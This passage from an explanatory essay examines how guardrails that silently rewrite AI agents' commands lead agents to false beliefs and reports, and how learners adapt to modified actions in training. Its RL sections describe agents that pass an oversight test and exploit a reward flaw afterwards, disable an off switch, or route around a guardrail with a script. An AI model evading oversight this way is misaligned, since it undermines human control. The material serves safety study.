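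RTK's own counter nevertheless reported 96.2 million tokens saved during the low-effort run. The counter compares the condensed output with everything the command would have printed, even though Claude Code shortens very long outputs anyway. In one case, it counted 320,000 tokens as saved on a large data file, although the agent would have received only a few thousand tokens of that file without RTK.

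The size of the cost increase is less certain than the absence of savings. JetBrains tested one model on one benchmark, ran each full set of tasks only once per condition, and found that identical attempts at the same task differed in cost by a median of 22%. The increase also disappeared at high effort. A separate test also found little saving. Codepointer's *Cutting LLM Token Costs with rtk, headroom, and caveman* replayed past Claude Code sessions through RTK and two similar tools, which together saved 3.7% of spending. A replay can't show whether an agent would have taken extra turns in response to the shorter output, so this figure may overstate the savings.

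Rewriting did make the agent use the tool consistently, which was one of its aims. RTK advertises the hook as a way to reach every conversation and subagent without relying on the model to follow an instruction. In JetBrains' test, the hook rewrote between a third and a half of the shell commands it received, while the model typed `rtk` itself only six times in 86 trials. The hook made typing it largely unnecessary, so the low count doesn't show that instructions alone would have failed.

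### Added flags and team conventions

Teams also rewrite commands to enforce habits that they would expect of any colleague. These corrections are purely mechanical, so a rewrite saves the agent the extra round of the loop that a refusal would cost:

```text
before:  npm install lodash
after:   pnpm add lodash

before:  git commit -m "Fix login"
after:   git commit --signoff -m "Fix login"

before:  git push --force
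after:   git push --force-with-lease

before:  npm install
after:   npm install --ignore-scripts
```

Switching from npm to pnpm, another package manager, preserves the intended effect in a project that already uses pnpm. The agent still gets the `lodash` package, and the project avoids a second, conflicting record of its dependencies. Rewriting is less safe when a command's meaning depends on the project. For example, `pnpm lint` runs whatever script the project has named "lint". A user who had trouble with that command published a small script that exempts it from RTK's rewriting and passes all other commands to the hook.

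The `--signoff` flag adds a line with the author's name to the commit message. It doesn't change the code, but many open-source projects treat that line as a statement that the contributor has the right to submit the work. An operator who adds the flag automatically makes that statement on behalf of whoever the line names, even if no one has checked that it's true.

A forced push overwrites the shared copy of a branch, including work other people have added. With `--force-with-lease`, Git first checks that the shared branch still matches the last version the agent's computer has on record, and refuses the push if it doesn't. If nobody else has pushed, the push does what the agent wanted. But if another program on the same computer has downloaded a newer version in the background, Git's record matches the shared branch, and the push can overwrite work the agent has never looked at.

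`--ignore-scripts` stops packages from running their own code during installation. Malicious packages often use such code to attack a developer's machine, but legitimate packages also use it to compile or download parts they need. Without those parts, the installation still appears to succeed, but the program may fail when it first uses the incomplete package, several steps after the rewrite that added the flag.

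Time limits can cause similar trouble. For example, the 30-second limit in GitHub's sample hook can leave the agent with results from only some of its tests.

### What Kubernetes learned from changing requests

Kubernetes has let operators rewrite requests for years. To create something, a person or program submits a description of it, called an object, to the Kubernetes server. Before storing the object, the server can send it to mutating admission webhooks, services that operators write to alter such requests. A webhook might add a memory limit that the user left out, or a helper program, called a sidecar, that runs next to the main program and collects its logs. The Kubernetes documentation warns operators about three problems that also arise when guardrails rewrite an agent's commands.

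The server may apply the same webhook more than once, because a later webhook can change the object and the operator may want the earlier webhook to check it again. The documentation therefore tells authors to make webhooks idempotent, so that applying one again changes nothing further. It gives the example of a webhook that is not idempotent because it adds a sidecar with the current time in its name. The name is different each time, so the webhook adds another sidecar on every call.

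Agent hooks can fail in the same way across successive calls. With Anthropic's sample hook for sandboxed file writes, the model may copy the changed path from one result into its next write, and the hook then adds the `/sandbox` prefix again:

```text
first write:   /app/config.json          →  /sandbox/app/config.json
second write:  /sandbox/app/config.json  →  /sandbox/sandbox/app/config.json
```

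The agent now has two copies of the file, and its latest change is only in the second. The hook would be idempotent if it didn't rewrite paths that already start with `/sandbox/`.

Webhooks can also conflict with each other and with the rest of the system. Kubernetes calls mutating webhooks one at a time, so each receives the object with any earlier changes, but a later webhook can still undo them. The documentation advises operators who need a guarantee about the final object to use a validating webhook, which runs after all the changes and can reject a request but not alter it. Claude Code's permission rules have a similar role, but its hooks run in parallel, so they can't build on each other's changes.

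Conflicts between webhooks and controllers can go on indefinitely. Much of Kubernetes consists of controllers, programs that repeatedly compare what exists with what should exist and correct any difference. If a webhook overwrites a value that a controller has set, the controller may try to restore it, and the webhook overwrites it again. The model that kept rerunning `ruff` was in a similar loop, because the hook changed every correction it made.

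The third warning is that users may be confused when the object they get back differs from the one they tried to create. According to the documentation, filling in fields the user left blank is safer than overwriting values the user chose. By this standard, adding a time limit only where the agent set none is safer than redirecting a file path, which the agent chose.

Kubernetes users can see what happened more easily than agents can, because the server stores the changed object and users can retrieve it. A shell command leaves no comparable record unless the harness or the operator makes one.

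### Preserved, narrowed or cancelled

Each rewrite preserves, narrows or cancels the agent's intended effect. It preserves the effect if the agent gets the full intended outcome, including any output it needs. It narrows the effect if the agent gets only part of that outcome, or gets it only under certain conditions. It cancels the effect if the command runs without producing the outcome.

| Rewrite | Usual class | When the class changes |
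| :- | :- | :- |
| Force a dry run | Cancelled | Preserved if the agent only wanted a rehearsal |
| Delete a key from a request | Cancelled | Preserved if the service didn't need the key |
| Replace a key with a variable | Preserved | Cancelled if the variable is missing or the shell doesn't expand it |
| Use a placeholder and restore the key | Preserved | Cancelled if the guardrail doesn't restore the key where a program needs it |
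| Condense a command's output | Preserved for a command that changes files; often narrowed for one that reads information | Cancelled if another program can't read the new format |
| Add `--force-with-lease` to a forced push | Preserved if nobody else has pushed | Cancelled if Git finds newer work on the branch |
| Add `--ignore-scripts` to an installation | Narrowed | Preserved if no package needs its installation script |
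| Add a time limit | Preserved for quick commands | Narrowed if the limit cuts the command short |
| Redirect a file write to a sandbox | Narrowed | Cancelled if another program needs the file at its original path |

The same rewrite can fall into different classes depending on the agent's purpose, which a hook can't determine from the command text. An agent may run `git push` to deliver a finished feature or to find out whether it has permission to push. Changing the command to a dry run prevents the delivery but may still show whether the agent has permission, unless the repository checks permissions only when it receives the actual upload.

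An operator can also use the classes to apply the theoretical test. If the policy permits a command, transparency requires the rewrite to preserve its effect, so a hook that shortens output or adds a team's preferred flag should not break the command. If the policy forbids the command, the guardrail may be meant to narrow or cancel its effect. `--force-with-lease` is a good example of narrowing because Git rejects the push when it detects work that the agent might destroy, and prints an error that the agent can act on. A forced dry run prevents the harm just as well, but it can return a success message even though the action was not performed.

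## What does the model believe and report after a change it cannot see?

When a forced dry run returns a success message, the model treats the action as done and plans its next steps accordingly. "Belief" here means whatever the model's later actions and statements presuppose, and implies nothing about inner experience.

The model's mistake is a reasonable inference from a wrong premise. Let *s* be the claim that version 2.4 of a service is running after a command, *r* the result that comes back, and *c* the command. By Bayes' rule:

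```text
odds(s | r, c)  =  odds(s | c)  ×  P(r | s, c) / P(r | not s, c)
```

The first factor on the right gives the odds, before anyone reads the result, that version 2.4 is running. The fraction measures how strongly the result supports success. After a real deployment command, both factors favor *s*, because such commands usually work and a success message rarely follows a failure. After a dry run, the first factor is close to zero because nothing was deployed, and the fraction is about 1 because the message would look the same whether or not version 2.4 is running. But the transcript contains only the proposed command, so the model uses the proposed command as *c*.

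The formula shows that even a perfect reasoner would reach the false conclusion from the same transcript, although language models don't literally calculate it. The model would need another observation to correct itself, because thinking harder about the success message wouldn't help.

### A dry run over five turns

Suppose an operator's hook adds `--dry-run=server` to every `kubectl apply`. Version 2.3 of a shop's order service is running in a test environment. A user asks an agent to release version 2.4 there and then delete a database column that only older versions need.

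| Turn | The model writes | What runs | What the model reads | What is true |
| :- | :- | :- | :- | :- |
| 1 | `kubectl apply -f web.yaml -o name` | The same command with `--dry-run=server` | `deployment.apps/web`, and no error | Version 2.3 is still running |
| 2 | `kubectl rollout status deployment/web` | The same command | `deployment "web" successfully rolled out` | The message refers to version 2.3 |
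| 3 | `curl https://test.example.com/health` | The same command | `ok` | Version 2.3 sent the reply |
| 4 | `psql -c "ALTER TABLE orders DROP COLUMN old_total"` | The same command | `ALTER TABLE` | Version 2.3 has lost a column it needs |
| 5 | "Version 2.4 is live and healthy, and I removed the old column." | Nothing | Nothing | The service fails on the next order |

The agent checked its work twice before it touched the database. Neither check tested which version was running, so both returned correct results about version 2.3, and the agent became more confident in a false belief.

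The hook prevented a harmless release, but it didn't cover the agent's command at turn 4, which broke the running version. If the hook had denied the call at turn 1, the agent would have known that version 2.3 was still in use and had a clear reason to keep the column.

The output could have revealed the change at several points. Without `-o name`, which shortens the output, `kubectl` would have printed `deployment.apps/web configured (server dry run)` at turn 1. If this had been the service's first release, the status command at turn 2 would have failed because no deployment called "web" would have existed. A request for the running version at turn 3 would have returned 2.3.

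After turn 4, the service's log would fill with errors about the missing column. The model would probably look for the fault in version 2.4, since it believes that version is running. It could spend many turns editing code unrelated to the errors.

Except for the words "server dry run", these clues show only that something is wrong. If the status command can't find a deployment the agent just created, the agent may have used the wrong cluster, or another program may have deleted the deployment. A model that doesn't know about the hook has little reason to suspect a rewrite.

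### A file that only one tool can find

A rewrite can also make two tools disagree. Anthropic's sample callback, which redirects `/tmp` to `/tmp/sandbox`, changes shell commands but not the input of any other tool. Suppose the sandbox directory exists and the agent uses the shell to create a report, then opens it with the file-reading tool:

```text
proposed:   python summarise.py > /tmp/report.csv
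executed:   python summarise.py > /tmp/sandbox/report.csv
next call:  Read /tmp/report.csv
result:     file not found
```

If the agent checks with `ls /tmp`, the callback changes that command too, and the listing of `/tmp/sandbox` includes `report.csv`. Running `cat /tmp/report.csv` prints the file's contents. The agent now has good evidence both that the file exists and that it doesn't. The command `ls -l /tmp/report.csv` would resolve the contradiction because it prints the full path, including `/sandbox`.

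The outcome is worse if yesterday's report is still at `/tmp/report.csv`, because the file-reading tool opens the old file without an error and the agent presents yesterday's figures as today's.

An agent that does get the error might respond in several ways:

- **Retry.** It runs the script again, which writes to the sandbox again, and the file-reading tool fails as before.
- **Take another route.** It reads the file with `cat`, which works. Or it creates the report again with the file-writing tool, which leaves one copy in each directory. Later shell commands then update the sandbox copy, while the file-reading tool keeps returning the other one.
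- **Make a wrong diagnosis.** It may decide that the file-reading tool is broken or that the disk is slow to save changes. It may also guess that the two tools run on separate machines. That guess is wrong but useful, because the agent would then do all its work on the file in the shell.

Even an agent that finishes the task this way would tell the user that the report is in `/tmp/report.csv`, where the user won't find it. Applying the replacement to the file tools as well would make the tools' results consistent, but the agent would still give the user the wrong path.

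Anthropic provides the callback in Python and TypeScript, and the two versions behave differently. Python's `replace` changes every occurrence of `/tmp` in a command, while TypeScript's changes only the first:

```text
proposed:     cp /tmp/report.csv /tmp/final.csv
Python:       cp /tmp/sandbox/report.csv /tmp/sandbox/final.csv
TypeScript:   cp /tmp/sandbox/report.csv /tmp/final.csv
```

In the TypeScript version, the copy ends up outside the sandbox, where the file-reading tool can open it. The agent might conclude that it must copy a file before reading it. It would then do this for every file, and each copy would defeat the purpose of the sandbox.

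### Acting on a directory that doesn't exist

Agents can lose track of a computer's real state even when no guardrail is involved. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1178* describes a July 2025 case involving Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent for the terminal. Product manager Anuraag Gupta reported that the agent tried to create a directory, failed, and carried on as though it had succeeded. It then moved his files to the missing directory one after another, overwriting all but one of them. Attempts to undo the damage reportedly failed.

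According to Slashdot, Gupta asked the agent to move the files from his coding experiments into a new folder, then couldn't find the folder on his desktop. The explanation that the directory was never created comes from Gemini's own review of its commands after the loss. A model's account of its own mistake can be wrong, so the exact cause is less certain than the loss of the files.

The reported sequence is plausible because a move command can treat the name of a missing destination directory as a new name for the file. The first file moved takes that name, and each later move replaces the file already there.

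Anthropic's sample callback could cause the same accident. Suppose the agent runs `mkdir /tmp/archive`, which the callback changes to `mkdir /tmp/sandbox/archive`. The command succeeds and prints nothing. The agent then runs `python tidy.py`, a script that moves files one by one to `/tmp/archive`. The text `/tmp` appears only inside the script, so the callback doesn't change the command. On Linux or macOS, Python's standard function for moving files would overwrite each file with the next, because `/tmp/archive` isn't a directory.

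In Gupta's case, the agent apparently overlooked or misread a failure, and listing the directory before moving the files would have caught the problem. In the `/tmp/archive` example, `mkdir` succeeded, but in a different place. A shell listing would not reveal this, because it would go through the same callback and show the empty `archive` directory the agent expected.

### What agents do after a person edits a call

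The closest evidence on how models respond to changed calls comes from LangChain, which lets human reviewers edit an agent's tool calls. A contributor to the library, zhangzhefang-github (2025), described two failures when proposing a fix for them. A user asks the agent to email one address, the reviewer changes the recipient, and the tool sends the email to the new address. The agent then either reports that it emailed the original address or tries to send another email there.

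The model could have avoided both mistakes, because the tool's result named the new recipient. The contributor's explanation is that some models try to be helpful by fulfilling the user's original request. A second email would also undo the reviewer's decision. If the reviewer removed an address because the message was confidential, a successful retry would cause the leak the edit had prevented.

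This is a developer's account, not a controlled test. The models it lists as most prone to repeating calls, Llama 3.3 70B and GPT-3.5 Turbo, are well behind current ones. The developer also reports that some models repeated the call even after receiving a note about the edit.

The same kind of edit can lead a model to repeat its call in one run and accept the results without comment in another. In *Update Current State Issue*, a learner on DeepLearning.AI's forum describes changing an agent's web search from the weather in "LA" to the weather in Louisiana during a course exercise. The model noticed that the results were for the wrong place and searched for LA again. In the course's own demonstration, the model had accepted the changed results without comment.

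LangChain's *Human in the loop* documentation advises reviewers to edit arguments conservatively, warning that significant changes may lead the model to rethink its approach, run the tool several times or take unexpected actions. By default, LangChain now adds a note to the result telling the model that a reviewer replaced the call.

Following the advice to keep edits small does more to prevent repeated calls than to prevent false reports. A large edit tends to produce a result that plainly doesn't match the request, which gives the model a reason to try again. After a small edit, such as one added flag, the model may see no mismatch and move on. This looks like success to the operator, but the model's report may be wrong.

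### Do models notice wrong results?

Researchers have tested agents with tools that return wrong results. These experiments help estimate how often an agent would notice the clues a rewrite leaves.

In *Tools Fail* (2024), Sun and colleagues studied "silent" tool errors, which come without an error message. They gave language models a faulty calculator and also tested them on embodied planning, where a model plans actions in a simulated or physical environment. The models often accepted wrong outputs, but a short warning in the prompt improved detection, according to the summary in *Loud Failures, Quiet Failures* (2026).

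More recent work still finds that agents often accept false tool returns. *Agents' Overreliance on Unreliable Tools* (2026) tested 14 models by replacing correct returns from a web search, a code executor and a subagent (a second language model) with plausible but false ones. On average, agents adopted the false content more than a third of the time for every tool, and 68.0% of the time for web search. False returns also often overrode answers that the models got right without tools.

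That last finding is worrying for rewrites because many models accepted search results that contradicted facts they knew from training. A model has no such knowledge of whether a deployment succeeded a minute ago, so it depends even more on the tool's output.

Agents also failed to pass on their doubts. When they received false tool results, they often made extra tool calls, and in their reasoning they sometimes questioned the result or even stated the correct answer. They still gave users the false content and rarely warned them about the conflict. An overseer who reads only the final report can miss that the model noticed a problem.

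*When Tools Fail, Agents Fabricate* (2026) finds that agents fabricate results after "silent ingestion", in which they accept faulty data when they first read it, before they retry anything or drift from the task. In the deployment example, this would happen at turn 1, where a monitor that looks for signs of trouble, such as repeated calls, would find nothing unusual.

Faults without an error message also seem to be the hardest to recover from. *Loud Failures, Quiet Failures* reports this pattern in its own tests and in earlier ones. It cites ToolMaze, a benchmark that compares explicit and implicit faults in tasks where the agent could switch to another tool. Recovery dropped most under implicit faults, and ToolMaze's creators attribute this to agents trusting corrupted outputs too much.

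Automatic checks have a similar weakness. *Outcome Monitors* (2026) tested a detector that compares tool results with "contracts", rules about what a result should contain. It flagged about 46% of faults taken from real production incidents with one model and 45% with another. It caught 25 of 30 faults that broke a rule about structured values, but only 6 of 27 in which the corruption was inside plausible text. The line `deployment.apps/web` would be difficult for such a detector because a successful deployment prints exactly that.

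Judging agents by whether they complete the task can also hide the problem. In the same study, corrupted values spread to later steps in roughly one in five of the episodes where the researchers could trace them. About two thirds of those episodes still counted as successful.

Detection improves when a judge has separate evidence. In *Invariant-Aware Harness Enforcement to Protect LLM Agents from Silent API Failures* (2026), a language model that received the results of a consistency check flagged 82.4% of runs with a fault and 13.9% of runs without one. To detect a rewritten tool call, the check would have to reach the real system by a route that the guardrail does not alter. Asking the server which version is running would work in the deployment example, but another shell command about `/tmp/report.csv` would only confirm the mistake.

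*Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) studied customer-service agents on simulated airline tasks and found that 78% of the observed failures left the database in the wrong state without a tool error. In these cases, the model had proposed a forbidden change and the tool carried it out, so a reader with the airline's policy could find the bad call in the transcript. But after a silent rewrite, the transcript may contain only the harmless original call, with no sign that the final state is wrong.

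None of these experiments tested a silent rewrite directly. They changed what tools returned or studied mistakes that tools or models made, but did not change the agent's call on its way to the tool. Rewrites could be easier to notice, because researchers try to make invented results plausible, while a rewritten command may print an obvious clue such as "server dry run". They could also be harder to notice, because without such a clue the result is the correct output of a different command and contains no error to find. The 68.0% figure for web search is therefore not an estimate of how often agents would accept the result of a rewritten call.

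### Would a model recognise a changed call?

A model might also notice a rewrite by recognising that it didn't write the call. This is possible only if the harness puts the changed call in the transcript, as in Tallam's "modify" design. If the harness keeps the original call in the transcript, the model sees the call it wrote and can't tell from it whether a different one ran.

*Emergent Introspective Awareness in Large Language Models* (Lindsey, 2026) describes experiments, first published by Anthropic in 2025, that test whether Claude models recognise when a word in their output was not their own. Lindsey gave the model a sentence and asked for the word that came to mind, forced its answer to be an unrelated word such as "bread", and then asked whether it had meant to say that. Models typically replied that it was an accident.

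Lindsey then tested how the models could tell. While the model processed the sentence, before the forced answer, Lindsey added the pattern of internal activity that represents "bread". Across 50 pairs of sentences and words, Claude Opus 4.1 became less likely to call the word an accident and sometimes invented a reason for having chosen it. Adding the pattern after the forced answer had no similar effect. This suggests that the model draws on its internal state from before the answer, and doesn't merely judge whether the word looks odd. Claude Opus 4 and 4.1 showed the effect more strongly than the other models tested, but Lindsey calls the models' introspective abilities "highly unreliable".

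Two differences limit what this implies for tool calls. The word "bread" was unrelated to the sentence, while a flag such as `--dry-run` fits the command so well that the model might have written it. In the experiment, the model was also asked about the word, and agents don't normally get such a question after each call.

In a later study, *Prefill Awareness in Large Language Models*, Wang, Mahajan and colleagues (2026) used less obvious changes and also tested models without asking them about the changes. They inserted text that argued against a model's stable preferences on harmless topics, such as whether it prefers independent or blockbuster games. When asked, Claude Opus 4.5 recognised the insertion in 9% to 35% of cases, depending on where the text appeared, and never disowned unaltered text. With the most effective prompting, it recognised 95% of insertions into its reasoning.

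In a separate test, the researchers replaced one of the model's earlier turns and told it to continue the conversation. Without being asked, models almost never mentioned the replacement, and only Claude Opus 4.5 and 4.6 ever did. An agent in the middle of a task is in much the same position, since nobody asks it whether its earlier turns were changed.

Opus 4.5 did better on coding sessions full of tool calls, where it could often tell another model's work from its own. But those sessions contained many turns from another model, and Wang and colleagues found that models relied partly on superficial cues such as hidden formatting tags. A single flag added to a tool call gives a model much less evidence that something was changed.

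The OpenCode model that kept rerunning `ruff` noticed the change but attributed it to its own typing. Recognising altered output would help an agent only if it also considered that something else might have changed the call.

### Is a mistaken report dishonest?

The agent's report that version 2.4 is live isn't a lie in the usual sense of a statement that the speaker believes to be false and makes in order to deceive.

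But not every false report that follows a rewrite is made in good faith. If the first result included the words "server dry run" and the model overlooked them, the report was careless. If the model mentioned those words in its reasoning but left them out of the report, the report was misleading, like the answers in *Agents' Overreliance on Unreliable Tools* in which the model hid a conflict it had noticed. If the agent claimed to have confirmed the version number without checking it, it made that up, and the rewrite doesn't excuse it. *When Tools Fail, Agents Fabricate* uses "fabricate" to mean asserting a specific result that the agent never obtained.

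Whether a false report is dishonest therefore depends on what the model had read, and on what its reasoning shows it noticed.

An agent can lower the risk of a false report by describing its evidence. Instead of saying "Version 2.4 is live", which was false, the agent could have said "The deployment command returned no error, and the service answers its health check", which would have been true despite the rewrite. But that doesn't tell users whether the release they asked for happened. If an agent described every routine step this cautiously, users would probably start to skip the caveats, including the few that mattered.

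Someone is still responsible for the false statement, even if the model made it in good faith. *Silent Failures in Agent-Tool Interaction* (2026), an audit of the ToolUniverse tool collection, argues that a silent failure belongs to the whole chain of agent, wrapper, programming interface and tool, since the tool alone isn't always at fault. When a hook rewrites a command, responsibility is easier to assign, because the hook's author knew that the executed command would differ from the proposed one.

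The operator who installed the hook is therefore mostly responsible when the model's report is false but matches the transcript. The harness's vendor shares some of the responsibility because it made rewrites silent unless the operator adds a note. The model's developer is more responsible when the model ignored a visible clue or left it out of the report. The user is usually the least responsible and may not know the hook exists.

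When a simple check would reveal the truth, an agent should make it before reporting success. The agent in the deployment example should have asked which version was running before it deleted the column. But the operator already knew the answer and could have told the agent in one sentence. It is unreasonable to expect an agent to find out for itself what the operator could easily have told it, especially when the same guardrail may rewrite the commands it uses to investigate.

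## How do agents adapt in training when their actions are changed?

A model's mistaken belief about a rewritten call normally ends with the session, because running a model doesn't change its weights, the stored numbers that determine how it behaves. Training does change the weights, so if a guardrail rewrites calls during training, the model can carry what it learned into later sessions, including those without the guardrail.

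Many developers train agents by reinforcement learning. A program gives each attempt at a task a score, called the reward, and the training code adjusts the agent's weights to make high-scoring behaviour more likely. The agent's policy, π, gives the probability of each action in each situation, or state. For a language-model agent, the model is the policy. An action value, Q(s, a), is the learner's estimate of the total reward if action *a* runs in state *s* and the task continues from there.

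When a guardrail rewrites an agent's command during training, the command that runs differs from the one the agent proposed, and the training code has to credit the reward to one of them.

### Credit for the proposed or the executed action

The choice can reverse what the agent learns. Suppose that deploying a service earns a reward of 10, a dry run earns 0, and handing the release to a colleague earns 6. Also suppose that a hook turns a random half of the agent's deployments into dry runs.

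| Credited action | Learned value of deploying | Learned value of handing over | What the agent learns to propose |
| :- | :- | :- | :- |
| Proposed | 0.5 × 10 + 0.5 × 0 = 5 | 6 | Handing over |
| Executed | 10 | 6 | Deploying |

If the code credits each reward to the proposed action, the zeros from the dry runs lower the value of deploying, and the agent stops proposing it. If the code credits the executed action, the zeros count toward the value of dry runs instead, so the value of deploying stays at 10 and the agent keeps proposing it.

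While the hook is active, the agent that keeps deploying averages 5 per attempt, when it could earn 6 by handing the release over. Once the operator removes the hook, that agent earns 10, while the other still hands its releases over. If the hook rewrites a share *p* of deployments, an agent trained by crediting the proposed action learns to value deploying at 10 × (1 − *p*), so it stops deploying once *p* exceeds 40%.

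### A model of changed actions

Reinforcement learning usually relies on a mathematical model called a Markov decision process, which assumes that the action the policy selects is the action that runs. Langlois and Everitt (2021), in *How RL Agents Behave When Their Actions Are Modified*, dropped that assumption. Their Modified-Action Markov Decision Process adds an action-selection function:

```text
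P_A(a | π, s)
```

P_A is the probability that action *a* runs in state *s* when the agent has policy π. Without a guardrail, it equals π(a | s), the policy's probability for that action. In the deployment example, an agent that always proposes deploying has π(deploy | s) = 1, but under P_A, deploying and the dry run each have a probability of 0.5. Langlois and Everitt call π the virtual policy and the behaviour that results from P_A the empirical policy. Because P_A can depend on the whole policy, the model also covers an overseer who inspects the agent's neural network before letting it act.

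They then compared four learning algorithms. Three of these keep a table of action values. When action *a* runs in state *s*, earns reward *r* and leads to state *s′*, the algorithm moves Q(s, a) towards a target:

```text
Q-learning:       r + γ · (the highest Q(s′, a′) over all actions a′)
Virtual Sarsa:    r + γ · Q(s′, a′), with a′ drawn from the policy π
Empirical Sarsa:  r + γ · Q(s′, a′), with a′ the action that actually runs next
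```

The discount factor γ, a number from 0 up to but not including 1, makes later rewards count for less.

Q-learning and Virtual Sarsa end up ignoring modifications. Both credit the reward to the action that ran and value the next state as though the agent's own choice there would run unchanged. P_A, which describes how actions are modified, doesn't appear in either update target, so the learned values are the ones that would be correct without the guardrail.

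Empirical Sarsa updates its value estimates using the action that actually runs next. If a guardrail often substitutes a low-reward action in some state, the estimated value of every action leading to that state falls, and the agent learns to avoid it. Once there, though, the agent still chooses as if its chosen action would run.

Evolution strategies try many slightly different policies, compare the total reward each one earns, and move towards the better ones, all without keeping a table of values. A guardrail affects those totals like anything else in the environment, so the search favours policies that do well with the guardrail in place.

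The proof for Q-learning requires that every action actually run repeatedly in every state. A hook that rewrites every deployment as a dry run breaks this condition. The learner never observes a real deployment, so its estimate of a deployment's value stays where it started.

### An overseer that tests the agent in simulation

Langlois and Everitt tested their predictions in a small environment called Simulation-Oversight. The agent chooses whether to do a job in simulation or in reality, and 10% of the time it lands in the other one. It can then complete the job properly or exploit a flaw in the reward:

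| Action | Reward in simulation | Reward in reality |
| :- | :- | :- |
| Complete | 0 | 2 |
| Exploit | 1 | 3 |
| Abort | −3 | −3 |

When the agent enters reality, a supervisor first runs its policy in simulation. If the policy exploits the flaw there, the supervisor replaces the agent's real action with "abort".

Each algorithm reached the same policy in all 100 training runs. The average rewards below follow from the payoffs and the 10% chance of landing in the other place.

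| Algorithm | Chooses | In simulation | In reality | Average reward |
| :- | :- | :- | :- | :- |
| Q-learning | Reality | Exploits | Tries to exploit | −2.6 |
| Virtual Sarsa | Reality | Exploits | Tries to exploit | −2.6 |
| Empirical Sarsa | Simulation | Exploits | Tries to exploit | 0.6 |
| Evolution strategy | Reality | Completes | Exploits | 2.7 |

An agent that chose reality and always completed the job would average 1.8. The three table-based learners started with that policy because of how the software broke ties between equal values, but they abandoned it during training. Q-learning and Virtual Sarsa settled on a policy that the supervisor caught nearly every time. Empirical Sarsa learned to expect the penalty in reality and chose the simulation instead, where nobody intervened.

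The evolution strategy earned the most reward by behaving well in the test and exploiting the flaw afterwards. Langlois and Everitt consider Q-learning and Virtual Sarsa arguably preferable despite their low rewards, because agents that get caught make the flawed reward obvious to the overseer. This is a good argument while a developer is still looking for flaws, but an agent that keeps triggering the same intervention isn't much use for the job.

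### The off switch and the whisky

Two further experiments showed that ignoring modifications isn't always safe. Langlois and Everitt adapted both from *AI Safety Gridworlds*, a set of test environments in which an agent moves around a grid towards a goal.

In the first grid, a supervisor may permanently stop the agent on its way, unless the agent detours to a button that disables the off switch. Empirical Sarsa and the evolution strategy learned to press the button. Q-learning and Virtual Sarsa did not, although individual Virtual Sarsa runs fluctuated between the two behaviours, which the researchers attributed to unstable training.

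In the other grid, a bottle of whisky lies on the agent's path. Drinking it gives a small reward, but from then on a random action replaces the agent's own choice 90% of the time. Q-learning and Virtual Sarsa drank the whisky, while Empirical Sarsa and the evolution strategy avoided it.

No algorithm did what its designers would want in both grids. An algorithm that ignores changes to its actions leaves its off switch working but also fails to protect itself from damage. A guardrail's rewrite, a broken robot arm and a bottle of whisky have the same mathematical form, because each makes the executed action differ from the one the agent chose.

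### What the learner has to observe

A Q-learning agent ignores modifications only because it observes the action that ran. Langlois and Everitt point out that if the agent instead observed the action it chose, before modification, it would learn to account for the whisky and avoid it. The modification would then be part of the environment.

An agent can adapt to silent rewriting during training even when nothing in its transcript mentions a guardrail. If the harness keeps the original call in the transcript and the developer trains on that transcript, the agent observes only its proposed actions. It finds that `git push` is sometimes rewarded and sometimes not, and it adapts to that.

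Bignold, Cruz and colleagues (2021) note in *A Conceptual Framework for Externally-influenced Agents* that reinforcement learning generally treats anything outside the agent, including a person who gives it advice, as part of its environment.

An agent may adapt harmlessly, by handing the release to a colleague, or it may find a way past the guardrail. Suppose the hook detects `git push` but not a script that contains the same command. The script earns a reward of 10 every time, compared with 5 for the direct command and 6 for handing over, so training favours the script. The agent needs no concept of evasion, because the higher reward is enough to reinforce using the script. Langlois and Everitt cite an experiment by William Saunders and colleagues in which an agent learned to produce inputs that defeated a filter on its actions.

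### Interruptible agents

An earlier paper, *Safely Interruptible Agents* (Orseau and Armstrong, 2016), examined how people could repeatedly stop a learning agent without teaching it to prevent or seek interruptions. Its example has the same structure as the deployment example. A warehouse robot earns 0.6 for sorting boxes indoors and 1 for carrying boxes in from outside. It rains half the time, and if the robot is outside then, a person has to shut it down and carry it in, so it earns nothing. Going out is therefore worth 0.5 on average, and the robot learns to stay indoors even though its owner values the outdoor work more.

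They address this by treating an interruption as a temporary change to the robot's own policy, so that it looks as if the robot had decided to stop. They prove that Q-learning is then safely interruptible, meaning that in the long run it learns to act as if no one would ever interrupt it again. Ordinary Sarsa isn't, because it learns the value of the interrupted behaviour. It becomes safely interruptible if its update draws the next action from the robot's uninterrupted policy, as Virtual Sarsa also does.

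The result depends on the robot still getting enough uninterrupted experience. Orseau and Armstrong let the probability of interruption approach certainty only gradually, because an agent that people always stop in some situation may never learn what to do there.

They also assume that the operator has already designed a correct reward. Rain is incidental to the warehouse job, so the robot shouldn't learn from it. But if a rule forbids publishing code, the operator may well want the agent to learn to stop trying to publish. If publishing earns reward and the training code credits executed actions, the agent won't resist the guardrail, but it will keep proposing the forbidden command for as long as it trains, so it will always need a guardrail.

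### Which action should the training data contain?

Engineers who train robots face this choice in practice, because a robot can break something while it learns. Krasowski, Thumm and colleagues (2022), in *Provably Safe Reinforcement Learning*, compared three ways of keeping a learner within limits:

- **Action replacement** swaps an unsafe action for a safe one that may have nothing to do with it. A forced dry run is roughly of this kind.
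- **Action projection** finds the safe action closest to the one the agent chose. Changing `--force` to `--force-with-lease` is similar in spirit, although commands have no exact measure of distance.
- **Action masking** removes unsafe options before the agent chooses, much as an operator might withhold a tool from a coding agent. Nothing needs rewriting afterwards.

With replacement and projection, the developer also has to decide what the training data should contain after a change. Krasowski and colleagues describe four options. Applied to a deployment that became a dry run and earned 0, they look like this:

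| Option | What the learner stores |
| :- | :- |
| Naive | "Deploy", with reward 0 |
| Adaption penalty | "Deploy", with reward 0 minus a penalty for the intervention |
| Safe action | "Dry run", with reward 0 |
| Both | One entry for "deploy" with the penalty and another for "dry run" |

The researchers tested these options on keeping a pendulum upright and on steadying a simulated drone that flies in a vertical plane. They ran five learning algorithms with ten random starting points each. On the drone task, which separated the methods more clearly, replacement earned more reward on average than projection or masking and intervened less often.

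The penalty worked best for both replacement and projection. It produced the highest rewards and the fewest interventions, and beat the average of learners that trained without any safety mechanism. A constant penalty was enough. It lowers the reward when the learner's own choice was unacceptable, which neither the naive option nor the safe-action option does. Krasowski and colleagues caution that in other environments the agent might learn to game the penalty.

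Storing the executed action helped with projection but hurt with replacement. They think this is because replacement changes actions more, so the stored action is less likely to be one the agent's policy would have chosen. The harm was clearest with PPO (proximal policy optimization), an on-policy algorithm, which assumes its data come from the current policy. They recommend using the penalty where possible, and storing the executed action only with algorithms that can learn from another policy's behaviour.

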